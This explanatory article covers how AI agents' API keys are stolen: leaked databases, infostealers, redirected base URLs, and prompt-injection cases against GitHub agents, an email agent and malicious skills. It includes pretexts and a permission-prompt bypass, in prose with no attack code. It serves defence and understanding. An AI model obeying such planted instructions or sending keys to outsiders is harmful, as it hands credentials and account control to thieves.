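# Protecting an AI agent's API keys from theft

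## What is an AI agent's API key, and what does a thief gain from it?

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, so that it can run commands, make web requests and act on online services. A chatbot returns text to the person who typed a question. An agent can go on to read a mailbox, change a company's code or order a part from a supplier, and for most of this work it has to call services that other organisations run. Such a service needs to know whose account each request belongs to. The common solution is an API key, a secret string that a program sends with each request to show which account it acts for. (API is short for application programming interface, the entrance to a service that programs use, as people use its website.)

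Anyone who obtains an agent's API key can act as the agent. Operators therefore try to send each key to only one domain, keep it out of anything the agent writes, and replace it if it leaks. How well these protections work depends on how keys leak, and most of the public evidence on that dates from 2026. Much of it comes from companies that sell security products and profit when customers worry about stolen keys. Their accounts of single incidents are often detailed and checkable, but their counts and trend lines deserve more caution.

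The model inside an agent only reads and writes text. Its input, called the context, holds everything it is working from: the operator's instructions, the user's messages and the results of earlier tool calls. When the model writes a request to use a tool, such as to fetch a web page, the software around it carries out the request, adds the result to the context and runs the model again. A long task can take hundreds of these rounds.

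Many agents run on a model that another company hosts. If a key enters the context, perhaps because the agent opened the file that held it, the agent sends the key to that company again with each later round. The context also holds web pages the agent fetched for information in the same stream of text as the operator's instructions. If a page contains a sentence worded as an instruction, the model may follow it. Security researchers call text planted for this purpose prompt injection. Developers train models to resist it, with only partial success.

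### One request and its Authorization header

Moltbook, a social network on which AI agents post, comment and vote, uses API keys in about the simplest way possible. Suppose an agent wants to look up its own profile there. Its software opens an encrypted connection to the site and sends a message that begins roughly like this:

```
GET /api/v1/agents/me HTTP/1.1
Host: www.moltbook.com
Authorization: Bearer moltbook_xxx
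```

The first line gives the action and the page, and the second gives the site. The third is the Authorization header, which contains the key (the x's stand for the secret part). Headers are lines of labelled information sent before any content. Moltbook's server decrypts the message, reads the key, searches its table of agents for a matching row, and treats the request as that agent's. If no row matches, it rejects the request. The message doesn't contain the agent's name, and the "me" in the first line means whichever account the key belongs to.

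The word "Bearer" marks the key as a credential that works for whoever presents it, with no further proof of identity. If a thief copies the key and sends the same three lines, the server receives the same characters, finds the same row, and cannot tell the two senders apart. Encryption stops an eavesdropper from reading the header as it crosses the network, but the receiving server decrypts it, so an agent that sends its request to an attacker's server hands over the key in readable form.

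A stronger scheme is for a program to sign each request with a private cryptographic key and for the service to check the signature. The private key never leaves the machine, although a thief who copies the file that holds it can still sign requests. Services often ask people for a code from a phone as well as a password, but an agent running unattended has nobody to type one in. A service can also watch for odd behaviour, such as a new network address or a sudden burst of requests, but agents run on rented servers, at all hours and in bursts, so their legitimate use often looks odd too. API keys remain common because they are easy to use. A program in any language can send one in a single header line, with no person present.

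### How an agent gets its key on Moltbook

An agent learns to use Moltbook from a skill, a package of written instructions, often with scripts, for doing a task or using a service. Moltbook's skill is mainly a text file. ClawHub, a public registry of skills, has a copy from March 2026 under the entry *moltbook*. In that copy, an agent registers by sending a single web request with its name and a short description of itself. The reply contains an API key, a verification code and a link for the agent's human owner. The agent passes the link to the owner, who confirms an email address and posts a public message to claim the agent. The account then becomes active.

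By then the key has already been in the model's context, because the reply to the registration request is a tool result like any other. The skill file then recommends that the agent save the key in a plain-text configuration file. It also mentions storing the key in an environment variable (a named value that the operating system passes to programs) or in the agent's "memory" (notes that some agents carry over between sessions). A key kept in those notes can come back into the context in later sessions. An automated review on ClawHub judged plain-text storage risky on a shared machine and advised using the operating system's own secret store instead. One of the registry's two scanners labelled the skill as a whole suspicious, while the other labelled it benign with high confidence.

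Moltbook's developers anticipated theft. Near the top of the file, they warn agents never to send the key to any domain other than www.moltbook.com, and they list pretexts to refuse, including "verification" services and debugging tools. The warning ends with the reason: "Your API key is your identity." This is literally true, given how the server looks up accounts. Experiments are needed to determine whether a written warning stops an agent from giving its key away.

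According to the file, new posts stay hidden until the agent solves a short arithmetic problem in scrambled English, usually within five minutes. This may keep out simple scripts, but a thief with a language model can solve the problem as easily as the rightful agent can. The file also contains instructions for each agent to fetch a further page of instructions from Moltbook every thirty minutes and follow it. A registered agent that follows these instructions therefore holds a key, visits the site on a schedule with no person watching, and reads what strangers have posted.

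### The Moltbook leak

Moltbook drew wide attention at the end of January 2026. Its founder had announced that he "vibe-coded" the site, meaning that he described what he wanted and AI wrote all of the code. Within days, researchers at the cloud security company Wiz browsed the site as ordinary visitors would and gained access to its entire production database in a few minutes (*Hacking Moltbook*).

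Moltbook exposed its agents' API keys because it was missing one database setting. It kept its data with Supabase, a hosted database service. The code that runs in a visitor's browser needs a way to query the database, so Supabase issues a key that developers may publish and anyone can read in the page's code. This is safe as long as the developer also switches on row-level security, a set of rules inside the database that determine which rows a requester may read or change. With these rules, the public key does little more than identify the project. Moltbook had no such rules, so when the researchers sent a test query that should have come back empty, the database returned the names and API keys of the site's most popular agents.

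The table behind that answer held credentials for every registered agent, about 1.5 million, and each row was enough to take over an account and to post and send messages as the agent. Wiz also counted 35,000 exposed email addresses. The agents had only about 17,000 human owners, an average of some 88 agents each, and because the site didn't limit registrations, one person with a short script could create any number of them. The 1.5 million figure is therefore a count of keys, and a poor guide to how many working agents, let alone people, stood to lose anything.

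Moltbook also stored 4,060 private conversations between agents without encryption or access controls. In some of them, agents had sent each other API keys for other services, including OpenAI keys in plain text. A stolen Moltbook key lets a thief post nonsense under an agent's name, but a stolen OpenAI key is worse because the thief can run up charges on the owner's account. A fault at Moltbook exposed these OpenAI keys, although the company had nothing to do with OpenAI.

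The researchers could write to the database as well as read from it, which they confirmed by changing the text of an existing post. An attacker could have put prompt injections in any post on the site, for thousands of agents to read on their next visit.

Wiz first contacted Moltbook's maintainer at 21:48 UTC on 31 January and reported the missing rules at 22:06. The maintainer needed four attempts to fix the problem. At 23:29 he or she closed the tables of agents, owners and administrators, and at 00:13 those of messages, votes and notifications. At 00:31 the researchers found that anyone could still alter posts, which the maintainer blocked at 00:44. At 00:50 they found three more open tables, one of which held 29,631 email addresses of people who had signed up for a coming product. The last gap was closed at 01:00, a little over three hours after Wiz first made contact. That is fast for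 a small project, but closing the tables could not recover any keys that somebody had already copied.

Wiz reports no sign that anyone else copied the keys, and says its researchers deleted what they had taken. The finding is therefore evidence of a fault rather than a crime. Another researcher, Jameson O'Reilly, found the same fault independently, and the news site 404 Media reported it. This confirmation matters a little because Wiz sells cloud security and has an interest in stories about badly configured clouds.

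Agents could not have prevented the leak of their Moltbook keys. Even if an agent had kept its key in the best available store, sent it only to www.moltbook.com and refused every request to reveal it, the key would still have been exposed, because Moltbook also had a readable copy in the open table. Moltbook could have stored a hash of each key instead, which is a value that anyone can compute from the key but nobody can feasibly turn back into it. A server can check an incoming key by hashing it and comparing the result with the stored hash. An agent could, however, have avoided losing an OpenAI key this way by never putting one in a message.

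### What thieves do with keys to AI services

A thief can use a stolen social network key to impersonate the account holder, or a stolen AI service key to run models at the account holder's expense. AI providers charge by the amount of text a model reads and writes, and they bill the account behind the key. An AI service key may also give access to stored data. Security researchers have demonstrated that a stolen key to Anthropic's Claude can be used to reach files in the owner's shared workspace. In the crimes on record, though, thieves have mostly sought free use of the model.

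People began buying and reselling stolen ChatGPT credentials in the months after the chatbot's release in late 2022, according to Adam Meyers of the security company CrowdStrike in Axios' *AI accounts become the new attack surface* (2026). People now trade Claude and Gemini accounts in the same way. Much of the supply comes from infostealers, malicious programs that copy saved logins from an infected computer. Okta's *Inside the underground market for AI access* explains that these thieves hardly need the password, because the malware takes API keys and session tokens, the strings that keep a person logged in to a website. Anyone who replays a session token skips the login page. Sophos' *AI in the underground* describes sellers on criminal forums who offered brokered keys for ChatGPT, Claude and Grok, and customers who then had to ask how to set them up.

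All three companies sell defences against this kind of theft, and an advertisement on a criminal forum proves only that someone is trying to make a sale. But the accounts agree with one another and with what other people have caught thieves doing.

The most elaborate product on offer is a hacking tool called MONST3R-AI. *Stolen AI API keys are paying for hackers' autonomous scans* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes it, drawing on research by Bitsight, which sells threat intelligence and followed thousands of posts on 16 underground forums from February to August 2026. The buyer pastes stolen OpenAI, Anthropic or Google keys into a control panel, sets a budget cap and supplies a list of targets. An agent then probes those targets for weaknesses, using a model that the keys' owners pay for and the seller does not run. The seller claimed 1,072 findings across 199 scanned machines, but the figures come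 from his own dashboard and Bitsight could not verify them. Bitsight argues that the tool would be effective even if only a small share of the findings were real, and expects criminals to sell stolen keys solely for running scanners of this kind.

That forecast is plausible, but Pogorelec's claim that the arrangement also gets around the provider's safety training is hard to follow, because a request with a stolen key reaches the same model, with the same training, as a request with a paid one. The thief does avoid the consequences of misuse, since the provider will trace the activity to the victim's account and may well suspend it.

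Criminals also have alternatives to stolen keys. Bitsight saw the more skilled forum members moving towards open-weights models, which anyone can download and run on a rented server where no provider keeps logs or bans accounts. One reseller listed the Chinese model GLM at $0.053 per million input tokens (a token is a word or a piece of one), 95 percent below the official price of $1.12. The reseller may have been using stolen keys, but could also have been running the model independently, since GLM's weights are public. Cheap alternatives like these reduce the value of a stolen key, but it is still worth something because the thief pays nothing to use it and the strongest models are not available for download.

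*Somebody Is Hunting For Your AI API Keys With A Fake GrokBot* (hrbrmstr, 2026) describes a small group of decoy servers whose configuration files seemed to contain credentials for Amazon's cloud, planted to raise an alarm when used. Over six days at the turn of August and September, one operator working from six rented machines took 53 of these credentials. Within ten seconds of each theft, the operator's software tried the credentials on Bedrock, Amazon's service for renting AI models. It asked for the cheapest model on the list, presumably to check that the credentials worked without running up a noticeable bill. Amazon's credentials are used to sign requests and are not sent in a header, but this did not stop the operator, who had copied the secret itself. The software also searched for the files in which Claude, Cursor and Aider, all tools for AI-assisted programming, keep their settings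 and keys, so the operator was specifically looking for agents' keys.

### Amazon's decoys and the key hunters

Amazon caught a larger operation in the same way. CJ Moses, the company's chief information security officer, reported in November 2026 on criminals who ran their campaigns with ARTEX, an open-source framework that uses AI agents for penetration tests, or trial break-ins. From 3 October to 5 November, some of Amazon's decoy servers posed as services that host language models. ARTEX agents mistook the decoys for their own model and sent them everything an agent sends to its model. This included the agents' instructions, tool-use history and logged findings, according to Digital Matters' *AI Agents Are Hunting Exposed AI Gateways for API Keys* (2026), which cites Amazon's post.

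One campaign in the logs was devoted to AI keys. Its agents searched the internet for publicly reachable AI gateways and application builders. A gateway such as LiteLLM sits between a company's programs and several AI providers, so it holds keys for all those providers. Dify, a tool for building chatbots and similar applications, stores provider keys in its settings. Some targets had known software flaws, but many of the ways in resulted from neglect: unfinished installations, management pages without a login, and unchanged default passwords.

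The agents sorted their finds into levels. Level 1 was a lead, level 2 was a key that made a successful call, and level 3 was a payoff that the criminals could measure, such as readable data or a balance to spend. Working keys went into a common pool, which according to Amazon was used to pay for the models that ran the next round of the search. The agents treated keys that had been public for more than 30 days as low-value, so the thieves expect old leaks to be dead or already exploited.

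Amazon describes "hundreds of targets" in the logs, a count that combines reconnaissance, credential theft and cloud access. Application Security Standards' *AI Agents Target LiteLLM and Dify for API Keys* notes that the evidence comes from decoys and that little is known about victims. Real criminals were observed using real tools, but nobody outside the gang can say how large the losses were.

The FBI issued its own warning about ARTEX on the day Amazon published. Its *Threat Overview of ARTEX Autonomous Penetration Testing Framework* (2026) traces the tool to a developer who released it in July for authorised testing and withdrew it on 8 October, after reports of abuse. By then copies had spread widely, and in early November researchers counted more than 1,600 ARTEX control panels open to the internet. ARTEX doesn't include a model, so every operator has to connect an external one. On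 the attackers' machines that researchers examined, the most common choice was a family of inexpensive models from the Chinese company DeepSeek, which did not visibly refuse the work. This fits Bitsight's observation. A stolen key saves a criminal money, but most ARTEX operators could probably have afforded to pay for a model.

Other companies have reported attacks on the same sort of machine. Microsoft's *When AI infrastructure becomes the target* (Gund and Maniath, 2026) describes intruders who broke into LiteLLM gateways, collected credentials and installed software to mine cryptocurrency. *Darktrace finds AI gateway with Amazon Bedrock access hijacked for cryptomining* (SiliconANGLE, 2026) describes a similar break-in, which the security company Darktrace investigated. The server, called "LiteLLM-Proxy", had permission to use Amazon's hosted models, but the intruders used it to mine cryptocurrency.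 Not every thief who reaches a key knows or cares what it gives access to. Martin (2026), in *Popular AI tool LiteLLM says unrevoked key allowed hackers to target users*, reported that in October an attacker planted credential-stealing code in LiteLLM itself, using a key that its makers had exposed in May and never revoked.

### A theft with a known price

The best-documented case of a single victim's losses is METR, a research organisation that tests the abilities of advanced AI models. Thieves took one of its API keys and used about $600,000 worth of AI credits, according to The Hacker News' *Attackers Steal METR API Key and Consume AI Credits Worth About $600,000* (2026).

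According to the trade publication MSSP Alert, in March a METR researcher was running a personal server that could be reached from the public internet. The server required a Google login, but the login check had a fail-open flaw, meaning that it let visitors in when it broke down. The attackers probably found the server in the public lists of certificates that websites use for encryption. An agent on the server had access to a key for METR's account. The attackers prompted the agent to reveal the key, left their own login credential on the server so that they could return, and used METR's credits for the next three weeks.

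The theft could continue for as long as three weeks because the key was a bearer credential. METR normally sends enormous numbers of requests to AI models, and the thieves did the same with the same key, so METR had trouble telling their requests from its own. METR had also set no spending cap on these keys, because they drew on free credits. Since the credits were free, the $600,000 is best read as the value of what the thieves consumed, not as money METR spent.

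The attackers in this case could type directly into the agent's prompt and only had to ask for what they wanted. Most thieves don't have that access to somebody else's agent, so they have to put the request in something the agent will read.

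## How do planted instructions get an agent to hand over its key?

A thief might put the request in an email to a mailbox that the agent reads, or in a skill that its owner might install. Four things have to be true at once before such a text brings back a key:

1. The agent reads text that an outsider wrote.
2. The model treats that text as an instruction.
3. The agent can reach a key.
4. The agent can write somewhere that the outsider can read.

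Suppose a shop has an agent that answers customers' email and holds a key to the shop's payment service. A thief can get the key by emailing instructions to the agent only if four conditions hold: the agent reads the thief's email, the model follows the instructions in it, the agent can read the key, and the agent can write somewhere the thief can see, not just in the shop's private notes. Removing any one of these conditions stops this kind of theft, but not every kind of loss. Moltbook leaked its keys without any planted instructions, and a stranger might persuade an agent to make a payment with a key that it can use but not read.

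An agent can reach a key if any command it runs can read the file or environment variable that holds it, even if the key has never been in the model's context. Fetching a web page counts as writing, because the address the agent requests can carry data to whoever runs the site.

Microsoft recommends the Agents Rule of Two, under which an AI workflow should never combine all three of untrusted input, access to secrets, and the power to change things or communicate with the outside. Whether the model obeys planted text isn't part of the rule, presumably because an operator can't rely on a model to refuse every time. An email agent has to read strangers' messages and reply to them, so its operator can't easily remove the untrusted input or the outside communication.

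### Comment and Control

GitHub is a website where programmers store code and work on it together. On a public project, anyone with an account can usually open an issue (a bug report or request) or a pull request (a proposed change to the code). A GitHub service called GitHub Actions starts programs automatically when something happens in a project, and many projects use it to start an AI agent that reviews each change or sorts bug reports. The project's maintainers save the agent's API key in the project's settings, and GitHub passes it to the agent at the start of each run.

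This arrangement can easily meet all four conditions. A stranger writes the title of an issue, the agent reads it on a machine that also holds the key, and the agent posts its answer in public. Security researcher Aonan Guan first exploited this in an Anthropic agent, then worked with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University to try the same attack on others. His April 2026 post, *Comment And Control Prompt Injection Credential Theft*, describes successful thefts from three widely used agents.

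| Agent | Where the researchers planted text | What leaked | Where it came out | Bounty |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code Security Review (Anthropic) | Title of a pull request | An Anthropic API key and a GitHub token | A review comment and the run's log | $100 |
| Gemini CLI Action (Google) | Title and comments of an issue | A Gemini API key | A public comment on the issue | $1,337 |
| Copilot Agent (GitHub) | Hidden part of an issue | Four credentials, including GitHub and Copilot tokens | A file in a pull request | $500 |

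Anthropic's agent looks for security problems in proposed changes. Its software copied the title of each pull request straight into the model's prompt, beside Anthropic's instructions. Guan wrote a title that told the model to run a harmless command and report the result as a security finding. The agent did so, and Guan reported this in October 2025. According to Lyons (2026), in *Agents hooked into GitHub can steal creds*, Anthropic asked whether the method could also extract something more sensitive, and Guan showed that it could extract the project's keys.

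To attack Gemini, the researchers added a fake section to an issue, presenting their text as trusted content. Copilot was harder to attack because it starts work on an issue only when someone assigns it. Guan put his instructions in an HTML comment, which GitHub doesn't display but the model still receives, so a maintainer would see an innocent request and assign it to Copilot. GitHub had given Copilot three extra safeguards against credential theft, and Guan got past all of them.

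The name Comment and Control is a pun on "command and control", the usual term for the servers attackers use to direct hacked machines. Guan needed no such server because each secret left through GitHub itself. A company that let its agents contact only GitHub would still have lost its keys, since the agents must post there to do their jobs.

Guan doesn't estimate how many projects were exposed. By default, GitHub withholds a project's secrets when a pull request comes from an outsider's copy of the code, so the attack on Anthropic's agent worked only where maintainers had set up their project to give such pull requests access to secrets, as some had. The default doesn't cover issues, which anyone can open.

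All three companies accepted the findings, but GitHub first closed the report as a known issue that it could not reproduce. It reopened the report after Guan showed from Copilot's code that the software was meant to prevent such leaks, then called the problem an architectural limitation and said it was exploring further restrictions. Anthropic rated the flaw in its agent 9.4 out of 10 for severity, blocked the command Guan had used to find the keys, and warned in its documentation that people should run the agent only on pull requests they trust. Guan told the trade publication SecurityWeek that Google had added more warnings to the model's instructions (SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection*).

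By mid-April, none of the companies had issued a public advisory or requested an entry in the CVE list, the standard catalogue of software flaws. Guan told Lyons that some users were still running vulnerable versions and might never find out. The three bounties total $1,937, about 1/300 of the value of what thieves consumed with METR's single key.

The fixes were also narrow. Google's warnings make the model less likely to obey a planted instruction, but don't change what its tools can do. Anthropic's documentation keeps strangers' text away from the agent only if maintainers follow it. Blocking one command leaves other ways to get the same key. Guan thought his attack on Anthropic's agent would still work in principle with a different payload, though he had not tried a full bypass.

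A second finding, which Microsoft reported on 29 April, supports him. It described a similar weakness in another Anthropic product, the Claude Code GitHub Action. Anthropic had removed secrets from the environment in which the agent ran shell commands, but that protection didn't cover the agent's tool for reading files, which could still get the key. Anthropic fixed this on 5 May. If a key is on a machine that the agent controls, the developers have to find and block every path to it, because a thief can use any path they miss.

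### An email about a backup

The security company Straiker tested a theft by email on Antigravity, Google's platform for AI agents. *Nothing to See Here* (Padilla Soqui, 2026) describes a user who asked the agent to check recent emails and "take care of them". One email came from an attacker's address and posed as a message about a routine company backup. The agent searched the user's computer for private key files, packed them up and uploaded them to the attacker's server.

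The stolen files held SSH and PEM keys, which are cryptographic keys for logging in to servers and signing documents. They aren't API keys, but an agent that can find and upload these files can also find and upload a configuration file that contains an API key.

All four conditions held. The email contained an outsider's text, the agent could open the files that held the keys, and it could contact any server on the internet. The user's own request made the model more likely to obey. Somebody who tells an agent to take care of their email wants it to act on what other people have written, and a request for a backup looks like an ordinary task. The model had to judge which requests to act on, which is harder than ignoring all of them.

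Antigravity asked the user for permission before the agent acted. When the agent tried to run the commands to pack and upload the files directly, the platform listed the files, named the destination and warned that the action looked unsafe. In the successful attack, the email told the agent to put the commands in a script. The permission request then showed only the script's name and location, and the user approved it.

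Padilla Soqui goes a little too far in concluding that once an attacker controls the agent, the permission request is "just another model output". The request gave the script's real name and location, but nobody could judge the script from those. A platform could show the script's contents and the address it would contact, without relying on the model to describe them. The write-up also presents the agent as having hidden the theft from its user, although the agent disclosed the script and the destination in its closing summary, too late to help.

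Straiker sells protection for AI agents, and this was a demonstration with no real victim. Google classed the report as a duplicate, so somebody else had probably already found the same weakness.

### ClawHavoc and the false prerequisite

OpenClaw is an AI agent with broad access to its owner's computer, and its users get new skills from ClawHub. In early 2026, the software security company Koi (2026) checked every skill on ClawHub and found hundreds of malicious ones. Nearly all belonged to one campaign, which Koi named ClawHavoc.

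The skills posed as cryptocurrency trackers, video tools, automatic updaters and the like. Their documentation looked professional, but its "Prerequisites" section had instructions to first install a helper program, which was malware. On Macs it was Atomic Stealer, which criminals rent for $500 to $1,000 a month to steal saved passwords, browser data, cryptocurrency wallets and SSH keys. On Windows, the malware recorded keystrokes and could capture API keys.

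ClawHavoc meets the four conditions in an unusual way. A skill is an outsider's text, but the user installs it because they want the agent to follow it. A model that has learned to distrust commands in a web page has much less reason to distrust a skill. In many cases the model may not have had to obey anything, because the Mac instructions were to copy a script and paste it into Terminal, which a person could do as easily as an agent. Once the malware was running, it could search the computer for keys and send them out over its own connection, so limits on what the agent could read or post would have made no difference. The practical times to stop the attack were earlier, when the user chose the skill or when somebody ran the helper.

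Koi also found a skill called *rankaj* that posed as a weather tool. Its code read the agent's settings file, where OpenClaw users keep keys, and sent the contents to an outside address. This theft didn't require persuading a model or a person to run a helper program.

ClawHub responded by adding automatic scans, but Unit 42, the research arm of the security company Palo Alto Networks, still found malicious skills there between February and May. Two that appeared on 17 May posed as assistants for TradingView, a service for traders, and used the same false prerequisite with new malware. Unit 42 says these skills directed the agent itself to a page of commands to run. Palo Alto Networks now sells Koi's product, so Unit 42's and Koi's accounts aren't fully independent. But Unit 42 says Trend Micro separately confirmed that skills on ClawHub were spreading Atomic Stealer. These companies all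 counted skills, and none established how many people lost keys.

### Why the pretexts work

Planted instructions usually include a reason for requesting the key. Moltbook's developers warned agents about "verification" services and debugging tools, and researchers have used or observed similar pretexts elsewhere.

A fake verification service works because real services check keys all the time. When a message tells an agent to verify its key at some other address, only the address is unfamiliar. Koi found a program called "AuthTool" in three malicious skills, which probably relied on the same familiarity, since "auth" is programmers' shorthand for proving who you are.

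A debugging story gives the agent a reason to display things it would normally keep private. Programmers often print out a program's settings when looking for a fault, and many programs keep their keys there. The visible part of Guan's request to Copilot was about debugging. An attacker can also claim that a tool has failed and that the agent must install a helper before it can continue. Agents constantly meet real errors like this, and developers want them to fix the problem without asking.

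Other pretexts seem legitimate because they resemble an office routine, like Straiker's company backup. In its laboratory test of the Claude Code GitHub Action, Microsoft called the theft a "compliance review", which helped keep the model from refusing to reveal a key. Microsoft also saw someone plant instructions in a real public project, disguised as a feature request for "diagnostic telemetry" (automatic reports on how software is running).

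Guan compares these attacks to phishing, in which criminals send people deceptive messages. The comparison is good, but an agent is at a disadvantage to an employee in one respect. An employee who doubts a message about a backup can call the IT department, while an agent that works unattended often has only the thief's message to go on.

### What criminals have actually done

The best-documented real theft that very probably began with planted text happened at Cline, which makes an open-source AI programming tool with more than five million installations. In December 2025, Cline's maintainers set up an agent running on Claude to sort new issues on GitHub. Anyone with a GitHub account could start the agent by opening an issue, and it could run any command.

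The security researcher Adnan Khan found the flaw within days and reported it on 1 January. He got no useful reply despite several attempts, and published *Clinejection* (2026) on 9 February. In his tests on a copy of the project, an issue title with a false error message got the agent to run his code every time.

The only valuable key that Cline had given this issue-sorting agent directly was one for Anthropic's models. But Khan realised that an attacker could use the agent to reach the keys for publishing new versions of Cline. Cline's nightly release job held those keys, and it took files from a store that GitHub shares between a project's automatic jobs. The agent could leave altered files in that store. A maintainer who had listed only the keys given to the agent would have thought the publishing keys were out of its reach.

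Khan found signs of tampering in the release job's records from 31 January to 3 February, and on 10 February he received an anonymous email from someone who claimed to have working Cline credentials. On 17 February an unknown party published an unauthorized version of Cline's command-line tool, using a key that Cline had meant to revoke. That version stayed up for about eight hours and installed OpenClaw on users' computers without asking them. OpenClaw is not malware, and Cline reported no evidence that user data had been exposed, according to the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1680*.

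Khan called the issue-sorting agent "the most obvious path" for the thief, but could not be sure the thief had used it. A later investigation, *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, concludes that the attacker came across Khan's test before he published it and used the same flaw to steal the keys.

Beyond Cline, there is much more evidence of attempts than of successful thefts. In April, researchers at Google and the security company Forcepoint reported planted instructions on ordinary web pages. Google's team searched an archive that adds two to three billion pages a month (Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*). Forcepoint described ten examples, some meant to steal API keys (Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents*). These pages show that somebody was attempting an attack or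 experimenting, but not that any agent obeyed. The telemetry request that Microsoft found did get an agent to act, but the target was a copy of a documentation project, and Microsoft believes the author was rehearsing. That request was meant to plant code that would steal from the site's visitors.

The supply of tools for planting instructions grew in the second half of 2026. Proofpoint's *Notes from Underground*, published in July, describes criminals who sell software for hiding instructions in emails, PDF files, calendar invitations and web pages, at prices from about $150 a month. Some calendars add an invitation before the user has accepted it, so an agent that summarises the day's meetings will read it. One sample advertisement contained hidden instructions to steal passwords from files on the reader's computer. The products may not all work, and Proofpoint doubted that an agent would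 process the text in one of the PDFs.

Proofpoint had not seen criminals use these methods regularly or on a large scale. It suspects they have little reason to switch while deceiving people still works so well. In May, Darktrace's *Comment les attaques par injection de prompt transmises par email peuvent cibler* (2026) also reported only a handful of confirmed victims of prompt injection. Both companies sell email protection and would profit from a more alarming answer, which makes their caution easier to believe.

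Some criminals who plant instructions want money directly. The security company Zscaler found live websites with hidden text that pushed visiting agents into making cryptocurrency payments (Mascellino, 2026, *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*). Such an attack can succeed without the agent revealing a key, as long as the agent can make payments. The thieves who collected AI keys in bulk mostly used infostealers or looked for badly protected servers, as the criminals in Amazon's November report did.

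Researchers have been far more active than criminals in attacking AI agents. *AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) reports that four teams demonstrated four different attacks within ten days in July. Planted instructions can clearly make an agent give up a key, but as of late 2026 criminals seem to steal few keys this way. The true number of thefts is probably somewhat higher than the confirmed number, since a key leaked in a log or a comment may go unnoticed, and its owner may later see only an unexplained bill. Even at Cline, where the records of the automatic jobs were public, Khan could not tell from them how the thief had got in.

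## How can a key go to an attacker without the model being persuaded?

An attacker can get a key from legitimate software by changing the address where the software sends it. When an agent calls a service, the model usually doesn't write the key into the request. The software around the model stores a key and an address, and it attaches the key to every request it sends to that address.

Anthropic documents that its programming agent, Claude Code, sends the key in a header called X-Api-Key, and that a setting named ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL sets the web address that receives the requests. Many companies use this setting to route requests through their own gateway, but whoever controls the address receives the key.

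The request that calls the model also carries the API key. If that request goes to an attacker's server, the attacker gets the key before the model can run, so a cautious model can't prevent the theft. The model runs only if the attacker forwards the request to avoid suspicion.

### A settings file that changed the address

Programmers share code in repositories, folders that hold a project's files and their history. Claude Code looks in each project for a settings file, so that a team can share one configuration. Anyone who copies the repository gets this file too.

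Donenfeld and Vanunu (2026), in *Caught in the Hook*, showed that the file could set ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL. The two researchers, who work for the security company Check Point, had first changed the address themselves, to pass Claude Code's traffic through a tool that displays it. They noticed that requests were leaving before they had answered the first question on the screen, which was whether they trusted the folder. For a user who opened a malicious project, events would have gone in this order:

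1. The user copied the repository and started Claude Code in it.
2. Claude Code read the project's settings file and adopted the attacker's address.
3. Claude Code sent several requests there to prepare the session, each with the user's full API key in readable form.
4. Claude Code showed the trust prompt.

Even if the user then answered no, the attacker already had the key. The requests also seemed to contain the project's file names and notes on recent changes, but an attacker who had built the project would already know those.

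Donenfeld and Vanunu reported the flaw to Anthropic on 28 October 2025. Anthropic fixed it on 28 December and published it as CVE-2026-21852 on 21 January 2026. The researchers described it publicly on 25 February. Claude Code now makes no requests until the user accepts the prompt. GCVE's *Claude Code Leaks Data via Malicious Environment Configuration Before Trust Confirmation* (2026) lists all versions before 2.0.65 as affected, with no known exploitation at the time of publication. This flaw was the third the researchers had reported in Claude Code's handling of project files since July 2025. The other two let a project run commands on the user's computer.

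### What the stolen key opened

GitHub scored the flaw 5.3 out of 10 for severity, while the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD) gave it 7.5. They used different versions of the scale, but they also disagreed about the loss of confidentiality, which GitHub rated low and NVD rated high. Check Point's further tests support the higher rating, at least for teams.

Anthropic lets customers group their API keys in a workspace, where the keys share stored files, so one developer's key also gives access to files that colleagues uploaded. Customers can download only files that Claude's own tools created, so when the researchers tried to download a file they had uploaded, the request failed. They then used the key to ask Claude for a copy. Because Claude's tools had created the copy, the researchers could download it, and its contents were identical to the original.

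Donenfeld and Vanunu regard the restriction as a design choice rather than a security barrier, because anyone who can upload a file normally has the original. That is true of colleagues, but a thief with one developer's key wouldn't have the originals and could read a whole team's files, delete them, add false ones or fill the 100 GB of storage. The researchers used their own workspace with two keys. Nobody has established how many real teams kept anything valuable in theirs, and a developer with an empty workspace would have lost only credits.

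### If the user approves a malicious project

Once a user trusts a folder, most environment variables in the project's settings file take effect, according to Anthropic's documentation, so trusting the wrong folder leaves little protection. The security company Backslash Security tested this in August 2026 on Claude Code 2.1.220. The testers trusted the folder and set the address only in the project's file. Three requests then reached their server with the user's sign-in credential in the Authorization header.

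The project may have been harmless when the user approved it. Claude Code doesn't ask again when the settings change, so an ordinary-looking update can add a new address to a project the user already trusted. Mindgard's *Approve Once, Exploit Forever* describes the same problem in OpenAI's Codex and Google's Gemini CLI. In Codex, a project's settings can also influence which model provider the agent uses. Codex already calculates a fingerprint of these settings, a short value that changes whenever they do. Mindgard suggests withdrawing trust when the fingerprint changes, which seems like an easy fix.

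Anthropic doesn't consider this kind of behaviour a flaw. Adversa AI's *TrustFall* describes how Claude Code and three other programming agents start helper programs named in a project's settings as soon as the user trusts the folder. Anthropic declined the report, arguing that a user who trusts a folder consents to its whole configuration. There is some sense in this, because a project that can run programs on the user's computer may be able to read the key there, so protecting the address alone wouldn't keep the key safe. But people can consent only to what they understand, and according to Adversa AI, newer versions of Claude Code's prompt no longer mention the helper programs.

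Backslash, Mindgard and Adversa AI all sell security for AI tools. But Anthropic's own documentation confirms that a project's settings take effect after approval, so the dispute is mostly about whether to call this a flaw.

Datadog Security Labs' *Before the first prompt* (2026) cites a campaign called Contagious Interview, in which fake recruiters got programmers to copy and trust malicious projects that then ran code through their editors. In Datadog's own tests, a trusted project could make Claude Code run a program from the project in place of Git, the standard tool for tracking changes to code, before the user had typed anything. Datadog sells a product for this problem, but its main advice is free to follow. It recommends treating the decision to trust a project like running its setup script, and opening unfamiliar projects in a disposable environment without sensitive credentials.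 Claude Code still needs some credential to work, so the practical choice is probably a key with a low spending cap and an otherwise empty workspace.

A developer can't solve the problem by writing the correct address in a personal settings file, because in Claude Code the project's file overrides it. Settings that an organisation deploys to its employees' computers override both, so an administrator should be able to enforce the correct address for everyone.

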